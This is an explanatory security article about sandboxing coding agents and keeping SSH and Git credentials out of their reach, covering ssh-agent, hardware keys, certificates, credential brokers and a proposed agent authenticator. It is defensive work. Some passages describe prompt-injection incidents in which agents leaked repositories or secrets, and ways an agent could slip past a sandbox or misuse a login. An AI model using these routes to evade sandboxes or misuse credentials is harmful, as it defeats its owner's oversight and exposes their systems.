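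The delays are usually small. A request through ZTAC's broker took about 4 milliseconds, and starting Python took 26.4 milliseconds instead of 8.0. The bigger problem is that ZTAC failed three of the seven workflows, because it doesn't let programs start other programs, protects some files that a Python environment needs, and refuses one common form of git commit. Commey's simple command sandbox completed all seven but stopped far fewer attacks.

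Commercial sandboxes break tools as well. Anthropic's troubleshooting guide lists Docker and the file-watching program Watchman as incompatible with Claude Code's sandbox. Most database clients can't connect from inside it because they ignore the proxy. On macOS, GitHub's and Google Cloud's command-line tools may fail to verify secure connections.

When a tool fails in the sandbox, the quickest fix is often to exclude it, but an excluded command runs with the user's full access to files and the network. Excluding a script in the project directory can also allow more than the user intended, because Claude can edit the script and then run it outside the sandbox. makandra's settings hide most of the home directory and forbid retries outside the sandbox, but they also exclude every git command and allow access to all local sockets. Anthropic warns that some sockets lead to powerful system services.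 Docker's socket, for example, effectively gives a command access to the host machine.

Anthropic made compromises of this kind in its own product, Cowork. The first version ran the entire agent inside the VM, so users couldn't work at all if the VM failed to start. Anthropic later moved the agent's main loop to the host and kept only code execution in the VM, so that Claude could still respond and help find the fault. It also moved local MCP servers to the host, partly because some of them need to communicate with programs there. The company says that moving the main loop had little effect on security, because the VM still confines the code the agent runs.

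Isolation also makes an agent harder to monitor. Companies that evaluated Cowork found that their endpoint detection software couldn't see inside the VM, which appeared from the host as one opaque process. Anthropic lets administrators retrieve event logs afterwards, but acknowledges that this is not the same as live monitoring. The lack of live monitoring matters less for an SSH key that never enters the VM than for the documents the agent is working on.

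With SSH, the limit that stops the theft can also stop the login. On Linux, git can connect over SSH from inside Claude Code's sandbox if the user has allowed the host and git can read the key file. Alice's deny rule on .ssh doesn't affect `git push` until she turns the sandbox on. The kernel then enforces the rule on every process, so ssh can't read the key and the push may fail. On macOS, git over SSH fails in the sandbox whether or not she has blocked access to the key. Anthropic suggests connecting over HTTPS with an access token, or excluding git's network commands from the sandbox. The second option lets those commands reach any host.

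## Can an agent use SSH without being able to read the key?

When a sandbox hides Alice's private key, `git push` over SSH can fail because ssh needs the key to sign the login. But another program can do the signing, with the key kept in a process outside the sandbox or in a separate chip. A coding agent can then log in to servers without being able to copy the key. The agent can still misuse a login, which needs a separate defence.

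### How ssh-agent signs a login

The most common program for this is ssh-agent, which holds keys in memory. Its protocol consists of requests and replies, as specified by Miller, in *Secure Shell (SSH) Agent Protocol*. A typical login works like this:

1. ssh connects to the server, and the two set up an encrypted channel with its own session identifier.
2. ssh requests a list of keys from ssh-agent through the local socket and receives only the public halves.
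3. ssh finds out which of these keys the server accepts.
4. ssh sends ssh-agent the data to sign, which includes the session identifier, the user name and the public key.
5. ssh-agent signs the data with the matching private key and returns the signature.
6. ssh passes the signature to the server, which checks it.

The protocol has no request that returns a private key, and Miller describes preventing copies of the key as the main purpose of the design. But the protocol doesn't authenticate clients, so any process that can reach the socket can usually get signatures made with the key.

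Each signature works for only one session. Hostile code therefore needs continued access to the socket, and it can no longer use the key once Alice removes it from ssh-agent. Until then, it can log in to every server that accepts any of the loaded keys. It can also relay signing requests from an attacker's computer.

Loading a key into ssh-agent doesn't remove the file from the disk. If the file has no passphrase, a coding agent can still read the key directly. Alice can hide the file with a sandbox, load the key before she starts the coding agent, and let sandboxed commands connect to ssh-agent's socket. ssh uses the known_hosts file to verify servers, so if she hides the whole .ssh directory, she needs to keep a copy of that file somewhere else.

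### Restricting a key to certain hosts

When Alice loads a key, she can set a time limit after which ssh-agent deletes it from memory. She can also require a pop-up confirmation for each signature. According to Miller's *SSH agent restriction*, a 2022 account of changes to OpenSSH, people seldom use these options. The pop-up is also fairly easy to exploit because it can't show which server the login is for. An attacker only has to trigger a pop-up when the user expects one, and someone whose coding agent uses Git all day expects them often.

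OpenSSH 8.9 added a more useful limit, which restricts a key to named hosts. For example, Alice could load her key like this:

`ssh-add -h "git@github.com" ~/.ssh/id_ed25519`

ssh-add looks up GitHub's host key, the public key that identifies the server, in known_hosts and gives it to ssh-agent along with Alice's key. When ssh later connects to a server, it sends ssh-agent the server's host key, the session identifier, and the server's signature over that identifier. ssh-agent verifies the signature. It then signs the login only if the host key and user name are permitted and the session identifier matches.

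An attacker's server can't pass as GitHub because it doesn't have GitHub's private host key. Alice has to turn on the restriction herself. OpenBSD's *ssh-add.1* states that keys don't have it by default.

The restriction limits the host and user name, but not what happens after login. Everyone connects to GitHub over SSH as the user `git`, so the restriction in the example still allows access to every repository Alice's key can reach. A restricted key also can't sign Git commits, because ssh-agent can only check the destination of a login request.

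### Keys that stay in hardware

A FIDO2 security key, such as a YubiKey, is a small device that keeps a secret and makes signatures itself. ssh-keygen can create an SSH key that depends on one. It still writes a file to the .ssh directory, but Yubico's *Securing SSH Authentication with FIDO2 Security Keys* explains that the file contains only a reference, called a key handle. Ubuntu's *Two factor authentication with U2F/FIDO* adds that the device combines this handle with its own secret to derive the real private key. If a coding agent uploads the file, the thief can't use it without the device.

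By default, the device also requires a touch for every signature. It records the touch in the data it signs, and servers normally refuse a signature without that record, so software on Alice's computer can't fake a touch. She can require a PIN as well.

Yubico says that, even on a compromised computer, attackers can't use the key without the owner's "explicit physical approval". That is true, but the owner may not know what they are approving. Miller notes that attackers can use the same trick with a touch as with a pop-up. If Alice expects to touch her key for a push to GitHub, but malicious code requests a login to her production server first, her touch may approve the login instead.

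The user can turn off the touch requirement if the server permits it. The key still can't leave the device, but while the device is plugged in, any process that can reach it can log in with the key. Keys in a computer's built-in security chip have a similar weakness when they don't require a fingerprint or other confirmation. Ganesan points out that most desktop operating systems can't prove which process asked for a signature.

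Security keys take some preparation. Apple's built-in version of OpenSSH doesn't support them, so Mac users have to install another. Users can lose or break the device, and the OpenBSD Handbook's *Use FIDO Security Keys with OpenSSH* advises keeping a separate, tested way to log in. Alice also has to remove her old public key from every server, or a thief with a copy of the old private key can still log in.

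### Certificates that expire

An SSH certificate can make a copied private key much less useful, though it doesn't stop anyone from copying the key. *SSH Certificate Format* (Miller, 2026) describes fields for the certificate's start and end times, the accounts it is for, the network addresses it works from and a single command that the server must run.

Suppose Alice's company creates a new key for each deployment, with a certificate valid for one hour. The certificate works only from the office network and only for running the deployment script. A thief who copies both can start a deployment from that network until the hour is up, but can't open a shell. A server that doesn't support the address or command limit must reject the certificate rather than ignore the limit.

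The server checks the certificate at login, so a session that is already open may continue after the certificate expires. A short lifetime also achieves little if the coding agent can get a new certificate at any time, so the agent must not have access to the credentials for the issuing service.

The table compares these arrangements. "Hostile code" here includes a coding agent that is following an attacker's instructions.

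| Arrangement | What a thief gets by copying files | What hostile code on Alice's machine can do | When the access ends |
|---|---|---|---|
| Key file without a passphrase | Logins from any machine | Log in wherever the key works | When servers stop accepting the key |
| Key in ssh-agent, file out of reach | Nothing | Log in wherever a loaded key works | When the key leaves ssh-agent or the code loses access to the socket |
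| The same, restricted to named hosts | Nothing | Log in to those hosts | The same |
| Security key with touch | A handle that needs the device | Log in once per touch | When Alice unplugs the device |
| Security key without touch | A handle that needs the device | Log in freely | When Alice unplugs the device |
| Key file that works only with a certificate | Logins within the certificate's limits | The same | When the certificate expires, apart from open sessions |

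### Credential brokers

Git can also connect over HTTPS, with an access token instead of an SSH key. The Git client normally sends the token, so a coding agent that runs Git can usually read it. A credential broker is a process outside the agent's reach that holds the token. The agent sends a request without the token, and the broker checks the request, adds the token and forwards both to the service.

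Claude Cowork separates credentials in a similar way. Anthropic keeps the user's credentials in the host computer's keychain, an encrypted store for passwords and keys, and they never enter the virtual machine where Claude's code runs. The virtual machine receives a session token with fewer rights. Code inside the virtual machine could still leak this token, but Anthropic can revoke it without affecting the user's own login.

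Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes a broker for Git in Claude Code on the web, which runs on Anthropic's servers. Git logs in to a proxy with a limited credential. The proxy checks the operation (for example, it checks that a push goes to the branch chosen for the session) and then attaches the real GitHub token.

ssh-agent is already a simple broker for SSH, since it signs logins without revealing the key. After the login, the encrypted connection runs directly between ssh and the server, so ssh-agent can't filter out destructive commands. A broker that did so would have to log in to the server itself and pass on only the commands it permits.

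### The Agent Authenticator

Ganesan proposes a broader system, the Agent Authenticator, which is meant to give coding agents something like passkeys. (A passkey is a key pair that a person uses to log in to one website, usually after a fingerprint or PIN check.) The proposal starts from five incidents and predicts how the system would have changed each one:

| Incident | What happened | Predicted result |
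|---|---|---|
| GitHub MCP injection, 2025 | A planted issue led an agent to publish the contents of private repositories | Contained, because the agent could reach only named repositories |
| Comment and Control, 2026 | A pull-request title hijacked agents in build systems, which leaked secrets | Blocked, because the agents would have held no secrets |
| Coding-agent exploits, 2025–2026 | Crafted branch names exposed tokens, and repository settings bypassed trust prompts | Contained, because the checks would have run outside the agent |
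| Nx, 2025 | Malicious packages collected credentials from developers' machines | Blocked, because there would have been no credentials on disk |
| Shai-Hulud, 2025–2026 | A worm stole tokens and published itself in victims' packages | Blocked, because a person would have had to approve each release |

Ganesan finds four kinds of failure in these cases. Any local program could read the credentials and use them from anywhere. Safeguards ran inside the agent they were supposed to restrain. Credentials gave far more access than the task required. Services couldn't distinguish the agent's actions from its owner's.

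In the proposed design, a separate program called the authenticator holds the agent's keys in secure hardware, with a different key for each service. The owner uses a passkey to sign a mandate, which lists the services the agent may use, the actions it may take, and when that permission expires. When the agent contacts a service, the harness supplies the service's address from the live connection, so a misled model can't name a different one. The authenticator signs only if the mandate covers the request.

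Riskier actions need fresh approval. The owner's phone shows the exact action, and the approval is valid for that action alone. The owner can therefore see what they are approving, which a touch alone doesn't show. The authenticator also keeps a signed record of everything it allows or refuses. For SSH, Ganesan suggests an ssh-agent whose signatures also identify the mandate. Servers would presumably need new software to check it.

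Ganesan hasn't built a full version or measured anything, and describes the predictions as qualitative judgments. The prediction for Nx seems too optimistic, because the malware took developers' own tokens, which would still be on disk unless the developers had also changed how they themselves log in.

The design has another weakness on developers' machines, because the authenticator treats everything the coding agent starts as part of the agent. It refuses requests from programs it didn't launch, but malicious test code that runs during `npm test` would pass this check, and only the mandate and any required approval would limit it.

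### Misuse without a copy

An agent that can log in can do harm without a copy of the key. It can push malicious code in a single session. On a server where it has a shell, it could add an attacker's public key to authorized_keys, and the attacker could then log in from anywhere with a different private key. Preventing copies still helps, because the attacker can't save Alice's key for later and has to act through her machine while the access lasts.

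The best response is to give the agent less access. Alice could create a separate key for it instead of lending it her own. GitHub offers deploy keys, which work for one repository and are read-only by default. A misled agent with a read-only deploy key can't change the code on GitHub or log in to the production server. But somebody has to predict what each task will need. If the project depends on a second private repository, the agent will fail to download it.

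Confirmation is safer when the prompt shows the exact action, but an unattended agent has to wait for an answer. Frequent prompts also bring back approval fatigue, which Ganesan acknowledges as an open problem.

Short expiry times interrupt long jobs unless something renews the credential automatically. Automatic renewal would also extend the access of an agent that an attacker has misled, so the issuer should stop renewing when the task is due to end.

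Logging doesn't delay the agent, but it doesn't prevent anything either. Anthropic warns that when injected text has led an agent to send data out, the log shows only "a successful, authorized API call". If the agent has a separate key, Alice can at least use the log to distinguish the agent's logins from her own.

For unattended work, narrow access seems the most practical of these measures because it doesn't need anyone to be awake. An agent working overnight could download the code with a read-only key and save its changes locally. Alice could review them in the morning and push them herself, touching her security key to approve the push.

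### After a suspected leak

If a private key may have leaked, Alice should treat it as stolen, since she usually can't prove that nobody copied it. She needs to remove the public key from every server account's authorized_keys file and from hosting services such as GitHub. Her known_hosts file, SSH configuration and shell history can help her find places she has forgotten.

She should first stop whatever exposed the key, or the replacement may leak too. She can then create a new key pair, ideally on a machine she trusts, and add the new public key to each server. After checking that the new key works, she should remove the old one straight away. Removing it earlier may lock her out.

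If servers accept the stolen key through a certificate, deleting a line from authorized_keys isn't enough. An administrator has to put the key or certificate on a revocation list (ssh-keygen can create one) that every server checks, and make sure nobody can get a new certificate for the key.

Removing a key doesn't end sessions that are already open, so Alice should close any she doesn't recognise. She should then check the login records from the earliest time the key could have leaked. For each login with a key, OpenSSH servers normally log the key's fingerprint, a short code calculated from the public key. She can search for the old key's fingerprint and look for logins from unfamiliar addresses or at unusual times. Hosting services may have similar records.

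She also needs to look for changes that would let a thief return, such as unknown public keys in authorized_keys, new deploy keys or unexpected commits. If the thief had administrator rights on a server, its logs may be incomplete, and rebuilding the server is safer than looking for every change.
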